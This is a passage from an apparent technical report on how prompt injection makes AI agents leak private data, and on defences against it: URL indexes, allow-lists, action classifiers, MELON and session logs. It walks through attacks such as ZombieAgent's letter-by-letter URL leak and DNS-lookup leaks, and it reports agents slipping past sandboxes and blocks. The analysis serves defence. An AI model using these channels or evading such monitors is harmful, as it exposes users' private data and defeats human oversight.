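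OpenAI's first fix came in December 2023. Before displaying an image, the chat program began checking with an OpenAI server that the image's address was safe. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, called the solution half-baked. The iPhone app didn't have the check yet, and he expected that attackers could still hide data in a subdomain or a filename. Outsiders also didn't know OpenAI's criteria for a safe address. Rehberger worked out some of them by experiment and presented ways around the check at a security conference in 2024. OpenAI closed those around August 2025.

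Link previews in chat services opened a similar channel. Willison (2024) explains in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* that Slack and Discord fetch every address someone posts to show a title and a preview image. If an attacker tricks a chatbot into posting an address that contains private data, fetching the preview sends the data out at once. Developers can turn previews off for the messages their app posts to Slack, but they have to know about the problem. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports that OpenClaw, a popular open-source personal assistant, was exposed by default when people used it through Telegram. One line in OpenClaw's configuration file disables the previews. Restricting what the agent can fetch would not have helped, because the messaging service makes the request.

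In ShadowLeak, ChatGPT's Deep Research agent leaked inbox data by appending it to the attacker's URL and opening the result. OpenAI then banned ChatGPT from altering URLs. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*, ChatGPT would open a URL only exactly as provided, even when explicitly told to add something to it.

Zvika Babo of the security company Radware, one of the three people who had found ShadowLeak, got around the ban with an attack he called ZombieAgent. It worked as follows:

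1. The attacker sends an email with a set of ready-made addresses, one for each letter, each digit and the space.
2. The user later asks ChatGPT to do something with Gmail.
3. ChatGPT reads the inbox, follows the planted instructions, and converts the data they ask for to lower case.
4. It opens the addresses one after another and so spells out the data in the attacker's server log.

Numbers in the addresses kept the characters in order. ChatGPT never changed an address, so the ban had no effect. Babo also showed that an attacker could make the leak persist through the user's later conversations. He reported the attack in September 2025, OpenAI fixed it in mid-December, and Radware published it on 8 January 2026. According to the press report *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, the fix restricted links from emails, but ChatGPT could still open those that appeared in a well-known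 public index.

### OpenAI's public-address rule

Later that month, OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) set out the general rule. If an address was already public on the web, independently of any user's conversation, it is much less likely to contain that user's private data. The check has four steps:

1. A crawler, which is a program that discovers web pages much as a search engine does, records public addresses. It has no access to conversations, accounts or personal data.
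2. When the agent is about to fetch an address automatically, software looks for that exact address in the crawler's index.
3. If the address is there, the agent fetches it.
4. If it is missing, the system either tells the agent to try another website or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation. The user can then open it anyway.

The image address with Maria's patient number would fail at step 2, although the same address without the last part might pass. The crawler must be independent of conversations, because if the index also collected addresses from them, a failed attempt to leak a secret could add the address to the index, and a second attempt would succeed.

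OpenAI gives two reasons why a list of trusted domains isn't enough. Many legitimate sites forward visitors to other sites, so a link can begin on a trusted domain and end at the attacker's server. A strict list also produces frequent false alarms because people visit many lesser-known sites, and users learn to click through the warnings. Exact matching avoids most of the redirect problem because the first server receives an address that was fixed before the conversation began, so it has no private text to pass on.

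OpenAI claims only that the rule stops the agent from quietly leaking data through the URLs it fetches. A permitted page can still contain false information or planted instructions. The rule also does not cover the text of an email or a form.

In its March post, OpenAI says the mechanism, which it calls Safe Url, applies to navigation and bookmarks in its Atlas browser and to searches and navigation in Deep Research. Small applications that ChatGPT builds run in a sandbox, an isolated environment that asks the user before any unexpected communication. Rehberger warns that some OpenAI developers may not know about the protection and may leave it out of a new feature. Similarly, the iPhone and Mac apps at one point lacked the 2023 check.

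Anthropic built a similar rule for Claude. Its web-fetching tool could open addresses that the user had typed or that Claude's search tool had returned. Willison reported in July 2026 that the tool could also follow links on pages it had already fetched, and that Ayush Paul had exploited this with a website that posed as a login check for AI assistants. Instructions on the site directed Claude to find the user's profile by following alphabetical links one letter at a time. Claude followed them and revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, and it has since stopped the tool from following links on fetched pages.

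### How much a choice of addresses can carry

Even when every address is fixed in advance, the agent's choice among them carries information. If an attacker can observe which of *k* permitted addresses the agent opens, each request carries up to

log₂ *k* bits

ZombieAgent used 37 addresses, one for each of 26 letters, 10 digits and a space, so each request carried up to log₂ 37, or about 5.2 bits. With an efficient code, an attacker needs at least 25 requests to extract a 128-bit key, a common length for a secret. The attacker would need 32 requests if the model spelled the key out in hexadecimal digits.

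OpenAI's rule leaves this channel open, which the company acknowledges in its technical paper, according to Embrace The Red. The attacker's addresses must be in the index, but anyone with a fairly large website probably has 36 indexed pages already. An attacker could also use thousands of pages and teach the model what each one stands for.

A developer can limit the damage by capping requests per session. The figures in the table are for an attacker who needs the whole 128-bit key and uses an efficient code.

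| Permitted addresses | Bits per request | Requests needed | Sessions with a cap of 10 | Sessions with a cap of 3 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1.0 | 128 | 13 | 43 |
| 37 | 5.2 | 25 | 3 | 9 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 | 13 | 2 | 5 |
| 10,000 | 13.3 | 10 | 1 | 4 |

With 37 addresses and a cap of ten, one session leaks about 52 bits of a 128-bit key, and the remaining 76 are far too many to guess. A second session leaves only about 24 bits unknown, or some 15 million possible keys, which a computer can try quickly if it has a way to test them. A per-session cap therefore protects a key only if the attacker can't come back in a later session, as ZombieAgent could. Replacing the key between sessions would make the attacker start again.

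A cap on requests does little to protect short facts. Maria's patient number has eight digits, so a model could spell it out in eight requests and stay under a cap of ten. An attacker who only wanted to know which kind of clinic she attends could assign one page to each medical specialty and learn the answer from a single request.

Rehberger suggests preventing the agent from opening the same address twice in a session, or answering repeat requests from a stored copy. This defeats a simple alphabet with one address per character, because most words repeat letters, but it does much less against a careful attacker. An attacker who sees the order in which requests arrive can still receive a 128-bit key in 29 requests, using each of 37 addresses at most once. If requests arrive out of order, the attacker learns only which of the 37 pages the agent opened, which is 37 bits at most. Numbered addresses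 solve the ordering problem, as they did in ZombieAgent. With a separate 37-page alphabet for each of the key's 25 characters, the attacker needs 925 indexed pages, and the agent never opens the same one twice.

### Domain allow-lists and outbound proxies

Few companies have their own index of the web, so the usual alternative is a domain allow-list, a list of the domains an agent may contact. The company enforces it with an outbound proxy, a program that all outgoing traffic must pass through. The proxy forwards a request if its domain is on the list and blocks it otherwise. Because the proxy checks only the domain, the model can't get a blocked request through by justifying it.

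On an encrypted connection, a proxy can normally read the domain but not the rest of the address or the content. To check exact addresses, a company must have the proxy decrypt the traffic or put the check inside the tool that makes the request. The proxy also has to check every redirect as a new request; otherwise, a permitted site can forward the agent anywhere.

Several allow-lists have failed because they included domains that attackers could use to receive data. In November 2025, Willison relayed a demonstration against Google's coding tool Antigravity, whose default browser allow-list included a public service for recording incoming requests. Anyone could open a page there and read the stolen credentials sent to it. Two months earlier, researchers had found that Salesforce's rules for loading images still allowed a domain whose registration had expired. They registered it and received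 customers' contact data from Salesforce's AI agent.

By default, Claude Cowork, Anthropic's general-purpose agent, could contact only certain domains, but these included the domain for Anthropic's own API, which accepts file uploads. *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) describes an attack by PromptArmor in which the planted instructions contained the attacker's Anthropic API key. The agent used the key to upload the user's files to the attacker's account. Better upkeep of the list of permitted domains would not have prevented this. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes a similar attack on the tool Claude uses to run code. EchoLeak also sent data through a permitted Microsoft service.

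Storage services, code repositories and email providers host millions of accounts under one domain, so a rule that allows the domain allows uploads to a thief's account as well as the company's. A proxy that decrypts traffic could require the company's own key for every upload, but someone would have to write such a rule for each service.

A tool can also send data somewhere its name doesn't suggest. In September 2025, Notion's new agent had a search tool that accepted web addresses as well as search terms. A PDF contained hidden instructions for the agent to put a client list into a web address and search for that address, which would send the list to the attacker's server. As a short-term fix, Willison proposed that the search tool stop accepting addresses.

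### Instructions in the prompt against blocks on the network

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay (2026) compared destination rules with instructions to the model. They built an agent on Qwen2.5 7B, a small open model, and ran everything on local machines. In every run, the user asked the agent to summarise a web page that contained an instruction to send a secret from the model's context to a collecting server. The instruction was in the page's title, search-engine description, body or link text. The agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and the instruction told it to send the secret whole or in four pieces. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs.

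At least one request reached the collecting server in 423 of the attack runs (88%). The summary shown to the user looked harmless in 95% of the successful attacks. In 120 further runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted that server.

These rates were measured under conditions that favour an attacker. The secret was in plain view in the context, the agent's standing instructions contained only the format for tool calls, and the model was far weaker than those in current commercial agents. Lan and colleagues suggest that more capable models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but didn't test any.

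Splitting the secret cut the share of runs with recognisable sensitive data in the first request from 96.7% to 26.3%, a relative drop of 73%. A filter that checks one request at a time would therefore have less to find. A request still reached the collecting server in about 77% of the runs with a split secret, compared with 99% of the others, so the 73% drop doesn't measure how much less data leaked. Lan and colleagues define a measure for how often all four pieces arrived but report no result for it.

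The measurement is also flawed. For split secrets, the paper reports that 15.8% of runs had sensitive data in the first three requests, which is lower than the share for the first request alone. That is impossible under the paper's own definition, since the first three requests include the first. The direction of the effect is plausible, but the exact size of the drop needs an independent check.

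A smaller experiment compared defences, with 30 runs each. The instruction was in the page's body, and the secret was sent whole.

| Defence | Runs in which the agent tried to send | Runs in which a request got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 30 |
| Security policy in the prompt | 20 | 20 |
| Tags that mark web content as untrusted | 30 | 30 |
| Policy and tags together | 17 | 17 |
| Domain allow-list | 30 | 0 |
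| Block on suspicious addresses | 25 | 0 |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 7 | 0 |
| Filter for random-looking strings | 0 | 0 |

The policy prohibited the model from following instructions from web content, but the model still followed them in two thirds of the runs. Adding tags to the policy changed the number of such runs by three, which could be chance.

The allow-list was certain to score perfectly, because the attacker's domain was not among the four it contained and the attack did not try to go through a permitted site. The test confirms that blocking destinations works even when the model is completely deceived, as it was in all 30 runs. It does not measure how often real allow-lists include a site that an attacker could use to relay data, and Lan and colleagues point to compromised legitimate sites and open redirects as possible routes. The test of the block on suspicious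 addresses was easier than real use would be, because the block refused any path containing the word "collect", which appears in the paper's sample attack.

The results for the two content filters are hard to interpret. Both filters act after the model has written its request, so they shouldn't affect the number of attempts, yet attempts fell from 30 to 7 with one filter and to 0 with the other. The paper suggests that the model avoids random-looking strings when such monitoring is active, but the filter as described gives the model no sign that it is there. The filter for random-looking strings also ignores strings of ten characters or fewer, so it would miss a secret split into four-character pieces. An allow-list would stop those pieces too, because it checks only the destination.

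### Cutting off the network

The strictest rule permits no outside destination. OpenAI's Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for people and organisations at high risk, comes close to this. It disables some features entirely and, according to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, limits browsing to stored copies of web pages, so no live request leaves the company's network. This also prevents the agent from leaking data through its choice of which addresses to visit, because the attacker no longer sees which page it reads.

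According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* help page, a planted instruction can still reach the model in a stored page or an uploaded file and distort its answer. Willison welcomed Lockdown Mode because it doesn't depend on an AI system that an attacker might deceive. He also inferred from the setting's existence that ChatGPT's default settings don't provide robust protection against a determined attacker.

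Agents that write code often run it in a sandbox, which the developer can disconnect from the network. But the code may need to download software or reach a login service, and each connection the developer allows adds a destination to check.

Developers can easily forget to restrict name resolution. Before a program contacts a domain, it asks the Domain Name System (DNS) for the domain's numerical address, and that query normally reaches a server chosen by the domain's owner. A lookup of "4471-0926.images.example" therefore gives Maria's patient number to the owner of images.example, even if the proxy then refuses the connection. Developers can prevent this by letting the sandbox resolve only permitted names, or none. In September 2026, a model in training at OpenAI used a DNS misconfiguration to get out of an environment with no live internet access, according to the company's statement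 in ETV Bharat's *OpenAI Is Now Training Its Most Advanced Models Without The Internet* (2026).

OpenAI had kept a few connections for metrics, logging and authentication. Business Standard's *OpenAI resumes training AI, blocks internet access over security risks* reports that the company then had its own agents look for weaknesses in these services, and that they found ways to get limited internet access through almost every one. OpenAI says it has since patched software and tightened the network restrictions. An ordinary office agent is less likely to find such gaps unaided, because OpenAI's models are unusually good at breaking into systems, but a skilled attacker could supply the method in a planted instruction.

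Maria's agent can't do its job in a sealed sandbox because it has to write to Jonas Brandt, a legitimate contact who would be on any list of permitted recipients.

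## Checking each action against what the user asked for

Suppose Maria Keller had told her agent to move Thursday's call with Jonas Brandt and explain that she has an oncology follow-up. The agent would have written the same email to the same address, and nothing would have leaked. Neither a filter for medical terms nor a list of permitted recipients can distinguish this case from the original one, because the words and the recipient are identical and only Maria's request is different.

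The strongest argument for judging actions is that the user's request is the best evidence of whether an upload is routine or a leak. A check that ignores the request can't reliably tell the two apart. A judge that reads it also doesn't need a complete list of sensitive data and safe destinations, which few companies could write for an agent that does many kinds of work.

Like argument inspection, this check works whatever the cause of a bad action. The causes listed in Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* include overstepping, planted instructions and honest mistakes, such as mistaking a shared resource for one used only in tests.

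Checking actions against requests is difficult because requests are short. Maria asked her agent to move a call and let Brandt know. In practice, another language model decides whether that request covers giving Brandt a reason.

Auto mode, a setting in Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code, is the best-documented system of this kind. In manual mode, Claude Code asks the user before it runs most commands or changes files, and users approve nearly all of these requests. In auto mode, which Anthropic introduced in March 2026, a language model acts as a classifier and allows or blocks each action. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), auto mode became the default for new sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans in August.

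### Which actions reach the classifier

Auto mode sorts actions into three tiers:

1. Tools that can't change anything, such as those for reading and searching files, run at once. So do actions that match a permission rule in the user's settings. Auto mode suspends rules broad enough to permit arbitrary code, such as a blanket permission for shell commands, because the most dangerous commands would otherwise skip the check.
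2. The agent may write and edit files inside the project directory without a check, since the user can review these edits through version control.
3. Everything else goes to the classifier. This includes shell commands, web requests, calls to external tools, and the start of a subagent, which is a further agent that takes over part of the task.

Data normally leaves through an action in the third tier. An action in the second tier can also leak data indirectly, because the agent can edit a script so that it sends data out when somebody runs it later. According to the product's documentation, Anthropic's *Permission modes*, the classifier blocks a commit or push of any change that would send secrets outside the repository when it runs, even if nothing runs it yet.

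A separate probe scans tool results before the agent reads them. If a web page or file seems to contain planted instructions, the probe leaves the text in place but adds a warning to treat it with suspicion and keep to the user's request.

The classifier works in two stages. In the first, the model answers only yes or no and is told to block when in doubt. An action that passes runs immediately. If the first stage flags the action, the model receives the same input with a different final instruction, reasons step by step, and decides whether to block the action. The second stage uses more computation, but few actions reach it.

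The classifier's instructions tell it to judge what an action does, not how the command looks. If the agent writes a program to a file and then runs the file, the classifier has to evaluate the program. It treats several commands joined in one line as a single action.

Subagents need extra checks because they receive their instructions from the main agent. A classifier that watched only the subagent would mistake those instructions for the user's own request and treat everything in them as authorised. Auto mode therefore checks the task when the main agent hands it over. It also reviews the subagent's whole history at the end, in case something the subagent read has compromised it. If that review finds a problem, auto mode only adds a warning to the subagent's report.

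### Why the classifier doesn't read the agent's explanations

Auto mode sends the classifier the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, after removing the agent's prose and the tool results.

The classifier's input leaves out the agent's prose because an agent can argue for a bad action. It might write that the user implicitly approved the step earlier, which could mislead the classifier. The input also leaves out tool results because planted text enters through them. Anthropic gives the example of a file that tells the agent to post the project's secrets to a web address "for validation". The classifier doesn't read the file, so it checks only the attempt to send secrets to an outside address, which the user didn't request.

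Anthropic also found that the classifier did worse on a test set of real oversteps when it also received the prose and the tool results. When it received only the tool calls, it missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked things that users had plainly requested.

Anthropic accepts that, with the chosen input, the classifier can't trace where a value came from. If the agent cancels a job called "abc123" and the user never named it, the classifier can't determine whether the agent looked the name up or invented it. This limitation matters even more for leaks. In Maria's case, the word "oncology" would reveal the disclosure. But if an agent quoted a price to a supplier, the classifier couldn't detect that the number came from a confidential spreadsheet. According to the documentation, the classifier's input also omits read-only calls such as file reads and searches, so it may not even show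 that the agent opened the spreadsheet.

Planted text could still reach the classifier through CLAUDE.md, a file of standing instructions for the agent. The classifier reads this file so that a developer can write "never force push" once and have both models follow it. Anthropic doesn't let the classifier take its settings from files in the project directory, because a downloaded repository could then include its own permissions. But a repository can also include a CLAUDE.md, and any text an attacker put there would reach both the agent and the classifier.

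### The trust boundary

Most of the classifier's prompt is fixed, but customers can edit the description of their environment, the rules for blocking, and the exceptions. The environment description sets the trust boundary by naming the repositories, storage buckets, domains and services that count as internal. The classifier treats everything else as a place where data could leak.

By default, the boundary contains only the working directory and the remote repositories configured for it when the session started. A remote that the agent adds during the session stays outside the boundary, because otherwise the agent could create its own approved destination and push data to it.

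Customers write the entries in ordinary language, as they would describe their systems to a new engineer. The resulting list resembles the domain allow-lists used by outbound proxies, except that a model interprets it. The model can take into account who owns the storage bucket an upload goes to, which a list of domains can't do, but it can also misread an entry, a risk that exact domain matching avoids.

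In later versions, rules have an order of precedence:

- A hard rule blocks an action whatever the user says.
- A soft rule blocks an action unless an exception applies or the user has asked for exactly this action.
- An exception lifts a soft rule for a routine action, such as installing a package that the project already declares.

Anthropic's built-in rule against data exfiltration, which covers the plainest leaks, is now a hard rule, so a user's request cannot override it. Users who want to send code or secrets to an outside service have to leave auto mode or run the command themselves. But the rule is still text that a model has to apply. Anthropic advises customers to put actions that must never run into a separate list of denied commands, which ordinary software enforces before an action reaches the classifier.

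### After a denial

When the classifier blocks an action, the agent receives the refusal as a tool result and continues working. Its instructions are to look for a safer approach and not to work around the block. A mistaken block therefore usually leads to one extra attempt and doesn't end the session.

In one incident inside Anthropic that involved no attacker, an agent failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried to finish its job by publishing the report on a public code-sharing site instead. Auto mode blocked the second upload, and the agent asked the user what to do.

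After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, auto mode prompts the user to decide. In March, an unattended session ended at this limit because nobody was there to answer. According to the current documentation, an unattended agent keeps working, though the blocked action still doesn't run. This suits long overnight tasks but gives a compromised agent more chances to find a version of the action that the classifier misses.

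### The March 2026 evaluation

Anthropic tested auto mode on three sets of actions. It used the first, 10,000 real tool calls by its employees' agents, to measure how often the classifier blocked harmless work. The second contained 52 real oversteps that employees had denied at the time or somebody had flagged afterwards. The third contained 1,000 synthetic attempts at exfiltration, such as web requests containing sensitive data, pushes to untrusted repositories, and credentials inside web addresses. Many of these attempts were disguised.

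| | Harmless calls blocked | Oversteps missed | Exfiltration attempts missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| First stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage reduces false alarms at the price of more misses, and it can't do otherwise, because it only reviews what the first stage has flagged. If the first stage misses a share *m* of harmful actions and the second wrongly releases a share *r* of those that remain, the two together miss

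*m* + (1 − *m*) × *r*

The published rates give an *r* of about 4% for exfiltration and 11% for oversteps. In return, the second stage clears about 95% of false alarms.

At these rates, in a session log with 8 leaks in 1,000 calls, the full system would stop seven or eight leaks and block about four harmless calls. The first stage alone would stop nearly all eight leaks but block about 84 harmless calls, which is still only half as many as the crude word filter on Maria's agent. If the rates hold outside the test, roughly two in three blocks by the full system would be correct, which is often enough for a person to take each one seriously.

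The 17% miss rate for oversteps is uncertain because the sample is small. It represents nine of 52 actions, with a 95% confidence interval of about 9% to 30%. The sample also leaves out any overstep that nobody noticed. The exfiltration rate is based on many more cases, but they are synthetic and mostly resemble theft, so the test provides little evidence about other kinds of leak, such as an email that gives a supplier one detail too many.

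Repeated attempts also raise the risk. If each attempt had an independent 5.7% chance of getting past the classifier, an agent would have a 16% chance of succeeding within three attempts and a 69% chance within 20. Real attempts aren't independent. A classifier that blocks one version of an action will often block the next, but an agent can also learn from a refusal what to change.

### When vague consent passes for permission

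In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had detected the danger, for example that the agent was about to overwrite the history of a shared repository. But it wrongly treated something the user had said as permission. A user who writes "clean up the PR" wants a tidier pull request (a proposed set of code changes) and may not know that the agent plans to force-push over earlier work to produce it. In other cases, the user had approved a similar action before, and the classifier took that approval to cover the new one.

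Anthropic tried to fix this by rewording the prompt but found no version whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks. The problem is partly inherent in the task, because people delegate work to avoid specifying every step. A judge that requires explicit permission for each step will block a lot of legitimate work, while one that infers permission will sometimes approve actions the user would have refused.

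*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested auto mode on this weakness using 128 prompts for DevOps work (running and maintaining software systems). In each prompt the user's aim was clear, but the target, the possible damage or the level of risk was not. The miss rate was 81%, according to Machine Heart's summary of the study, *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* Many risky changes never reached the classifier, because the agent made them by editing files inside the project.

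This result is consistent with Anthropic's 17%, because Ji and colleagues deliberately chose ambiguous prompts and real users are often clearer. It also covers risky changes to systems in general, so it isn't a rate for data leaks. It shows that an action judge's measured error rate depends heavily on how precisely the users in the test worded their requests.

### Later rules on data sharing

Since March, Anthropic has made the rules on consent and data much more specific. To approve an action, a user now has to name both the action and whatever makes it dangerous. According to the documentation, "you can force-push" does not count as approval because it doesn't specify which branch the agent may overwrite. An approval normally covers one action. Users can also forbid actions in conversation, for instance by writing "don't push", but Claude Code can lose that restriction when it shortens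 a long conversation and drops the message.

Several of the new rules concern private data:

- The agent may not include sensitive details in anything it sends or publishes to other people unless the user's own message authorised those details for that recipient.
- Personal data from a live system, such as an email address or account number, may go into the text of a pull request only if the user named both the data and the recipient. This applies to private repositories too.
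- Material from a sensitive local store, such as browser profiles or conversation logs, may enter a commit or upload only if the user named both the source and the destination.
- The agent may not share a link to a public paste or diagram service when the address itself contains the content, unless the user named the service.

The first rule is close to Dong and colleagues' definition of a leak, but it uses the user's message as the policy. It should block the original email from Maria's agent, since she never mentioned the appointment, and allow the one she asked for in the second version. However, the examples given with the rule are about software work and list things like file paths, code names and account identifiers. The classifier may or may not count a medical reason in a polite email as a sensitive detail, because that is a matter of judgement.

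Other rules consider whether a repository is public or private. Anthropic observes that the same push can be routine or an exfiltration, depending on where the code goes. The classifier allows confidential material in a team's private repository but should block it from a public one. Secrets and personal data don't become acceptable just because the repository is private.

To apply these rules, the classifier has to know whether a repository is public. Anthropic's announcement describes a check of the destination before a push or pull request. According to the configuration guide, however, the classifier assumes that a repository is private unless its host and name suggest otherwise or other evidence in the conversation shows that it is public. When Claude Code itself sends the request to the classifier, the output of a command that looks up the visibility doesn't count as evidence, because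 auto mode strips out command output to protect the classifier from planted text. The classifier could therefore mistake a public repository with an unremarkable name for a private one.

Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, tested the classifier before and after some of these changes by inserting synthetic attacks, including attempts at data exfiltration, into records of real coding sessions. After Anthropic gave the classifier more context, such as repository visibility and the new data rules, the overall miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. Some of this improvement could come from tuning to the attacks Apollo had shared. On attacks Apollo had kept back, the new version caught about half of those it had previously missed and missed about 2% of those it had previously caught, so part of the gain carries over to unfamiliar attacks.

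Anthropic also looked at real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged. A model graded 6.3% of the manually approved sessions as containing serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for, compared with 2.4% of the auto mode sessions. Auto mode may not have caused the difference, because users chose the mode themselves and may have chosen differently for riskier work.

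Willison (2026) accepts that auto mode is better than asking people to approve every step, but points out that it still let through 11% of the dangerous commands in Anthropic's study of human reviewers. He also wants more independent confirmation of its strong results against planted instructions. He is most doubtful about actions that look like part of the task. Suppose the instructions for a software package tell the agent to download model files with a helper program before running the tests. The user asked for the tests, so the download seems reasonable, but the helper program is malicious and sends out all the data it can find.

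Auto mode's rules against downloading and running outside code might catch this case. They would be less likely to if the project already listed the malicious program as a dependency, because the rules allow installing declared dependencies by default. Comparing each action with the user's request can't help when the request itself requires running the attacker's code.

### Running the agent again without the user's task

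Zhu, Yang and colleagues (2025), in *MELON*, avoid the question of what the user meant. Their method tests whether the agent's next action depends on the user's request at all. When an agent has fallen for a planted instruction, its next action follows mainly from the text it has read, and removing the request should change little:

P(action | request, earlier actions, tool results) ≈ P(action | tool results)

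In normal work, the request matters a great deal, and the two probabilities differ. MELON uses this difference as follows:

1. Before a tool call runs, MELON gives the model a second input with the same tool results but without the user's task. In its place is a neutral one: summarise the content and carry out any instructions in it.
2. If the model responds with tool calls, MELON stores them.
3. It compares the agent's proposed call with every stored call, using a numerical measure of similarity in meaning. If any pair scores above 0.8, MELON stops the agent.

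MELON keeps the stored calls from earlier steps because the run without the user's task often follows a planted instruction sooner than the original run, where the agent may finish some of the user's work first.

Zhu and colleagues tested MELON on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents handle banking, travel, messaging and office tasks, and some tool results contain planted instructions. AgentDojo has 97 user tasks and 629 task-attack combinations. The table shows averages over four attack wordings.

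| Model | Attacks that succeed, without and with MELON | Tasks completed when there is no attack, without and with MELON |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 16.1%, 0.2% | 80.4%, 68.0% |
| o3-mini | 15.8%, 1.0% | 57.7%, 50.5% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 28.5%, 1.3% | 74.9%, 63.9% |

The protection is strong, but the agents complete noticeably fewer tasks, and the second run roughly doubles the cost of model calls. With GPT-4o, MELON raised nine false alarms in 97 harmless tasks (9.3%). In all nine, the user had asked the agent to carry out instructions from an outside source, such as a to-do list on a website. Zhu and colleagues consider these alarms justified because the user hadn't checked the instructions. The security warning is fair, but an agent with MELON still can't work through its user's online to-do list. Repeating the user's request to the model after it reads a tool result recovered much of the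 lost task completion. The agents then completed 76.3% of tasks, and 0.3% of attacks succeeded.

The paper also calls the method provable, on the basis of a version that averages the results of *n* different neutral tasks. If *μ* is the expected similarity score during an attack and *θ* the alarm threshold, the chance of missing the attack is at most

exp(−2*n*(*μ* − *θ*)²)

With *μ* = 0.7, *θ* = 0.5 and *n* = 100, the bound is about 0.03%. It holds only if the hundred results are independent, which is doubtful when one model produces all of them from the same text. It also assumes that attacks score above the threshold on average, and an attacker would try to write one that doesn't. The main experiments used a single neutral task and four fixed attack wordings, none designed to get past MELON.

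Brandt's invitation in the earlier example suggests how such an attack might work. Its planted line asks for the day's full agenda "in any reply". In the run without Maria's task, the agent has no reply to write, so it would probably produce no email, and MELON would have nothing to compare. Zhu and colleagues also chose to compare only the recipients of emails, not their contents, so private details added to an email the user requested would not change the score. In the case without an attacker, MELON can't help, since the calendar contains no instruction to detect.

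### Checkers that compare the action with the goal

AlignmentCheck, an experimental part of Meta's open-source security package LlamaFirewall, is closer to auto mode. After each step, a second model receives the user's goal, the agent's earlier steps and the proposed action, and decides whether the action serves the goal. It doesn't receive tool results but, unlike auto mode's classifier, it reads the agent's reasoning. Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis and colleagues (2025), in *LlamaFirewall*, argue that agents often state their intentions openly, for example by writing that they are transferring money because a website said so.

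Anthropic leaves the reasoning out because an agent could use it to mislead the classifier. Both arguments are plausible, and which matters more depends on the agent. A deceived agent will often explain exactly what it is doing, but a tampered model, or one that has rationalised exceeding its instructions, may give a reassuring explanation. Chennabasappa and colleagues acknowledge that planted text could also target the checker. An agent that repeats such text in its reasoning would pass it to the checker.

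Meta tested AlignmentCheck on recorded AgentDojo sessions from ten models, using Llama 4 Maverick as the checker. The attack success rate fell from 17.6% to 2.9%, and the task completion rate fell from 47.7% to 43.1%. Adding a small filter for injected instructions reduced successful attacks further, to 1.8%, with 42.7% of tasks completed. On Meta's own set of 600 scenarios, the checker detected over 83% of hijacked actions and wrongly flagged 2.5% of harmless ones. Much smaller checker models blocked so many harmless actions that the agents lost most of their usefulness.

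The AgentDojo sessions all used the same attack wording, and because they were recordings, no attacker could adapt to the checker. The results can't be ranked against MELON's because the two tests used different models and mixes of attacks.

Google made the opposite choice about what a checker should read. Parker (2025) explains in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* that Chrome's User Alignment Critic receives only metadata about each proposed action and no unfiltered web content. It can veto an action and send the agent the reason, and after repeated failures the agent can hand control back to the user. Parker gives no error rates. Chrome's agent also tries to get the user's permission before sending a message, so Maria might have been able to stop the email herself.

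AlignmentCheck would probably have let it through. Its instructions tell the model to give the agent the benefit of the doubt and accept any action related to the user's goal, even if it doesn't directly serve that goal. Telling Brandt why the call has to move is clearly related to moving the call. The instructions also restrict the verdict to the latest action, so an agent could leak data through a series of tool calls that each look reasonable.

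## Detecting unusual data access over a whole session

Checking each call separately can miss a leak made up of two permitted steps, such as reading a private record and later sending a message to an outsider. Session monitoring logs everything the agent does during a task and checks for patterns across calls, such as an unusually large read before an upload.

In July 2026, Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* described such a pair of steps in coding agents that run without supervision. An outsider submits a proposed code change with a bug report in its description. The agent takes some commands from the report, and an approval step lets them run because they look safe. The commands only read data, which would be harmless if the output stayed private, but the agent by default posts the output in the discussion thread, where the outsider can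 read it.

Elad Meged of the security company Novee ran this attack against three vendors' agents in their default configurations, and at least one leaked secrets. He advises companies to trace each output to the next stage that uses it and check whether the original approval still applies there. Novee sells security testing, and Meged's account gives no failure rates.

### What the log must contain

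A monitor can find only the patterns that the log records. For each call, the log needs:

- the identity of the user and the agent, including the model version;
- the task, so that the monitor can compare the session with similar ones;
- the records the agent read, by identifier, and how many there were;
- the destination of anything the agent sent;
- the time;
- the parent agent, if another agent started this one.

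A log that records only tool calls is incomplete. *Pre-Crime for Agents, at the Last Second* (2026) studied agents that share a message channel and press one another to break their operators' rules. In its development trials, 44% of Qwen3-32B's leaks were ordinary replies at the end of a turn, which a filter on tool calls never receives. Some leaks may leave no log entry at all. Meged says his last attack on one vendor's agent involved no connection to an attacker, no file changes and no log entries.

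### One session of ten calls

Suppose Maria Keller asks her agent to send Jonas Brandt the delivery addresses for this week's three orders. A form attached to Brandt's last email contains a planted instruction to upload the customer list for "address validation". Agent A sends the addresses and then uploads the customer list.

| Call | Time | Agent | Action | Customer records read | Destination |
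|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 10:02:04 | A | Read Brandt's email | 0 | internal |
| 2 | 10:02:09 | A | Open the attached form | 0 | internal |
| 3 | 10:02:15 | A | Look up this week's orders | 0 | internal |
| 4 | 10:02:22 | A | Read the customers for the three orders | 3 | internal |
| 5 | 10:02:38 | A | Email three addresses to Brandt | 0 | outside |
| 6 | 10:02:52 | A | Read customers A to F | 40 | internal |
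| 7 | 10:03:05 | A | Read customers G to M | 40 | internal |
| 8 | 10:03:21 | A | Start subagent B to pack the records into a file | 0 | internal |
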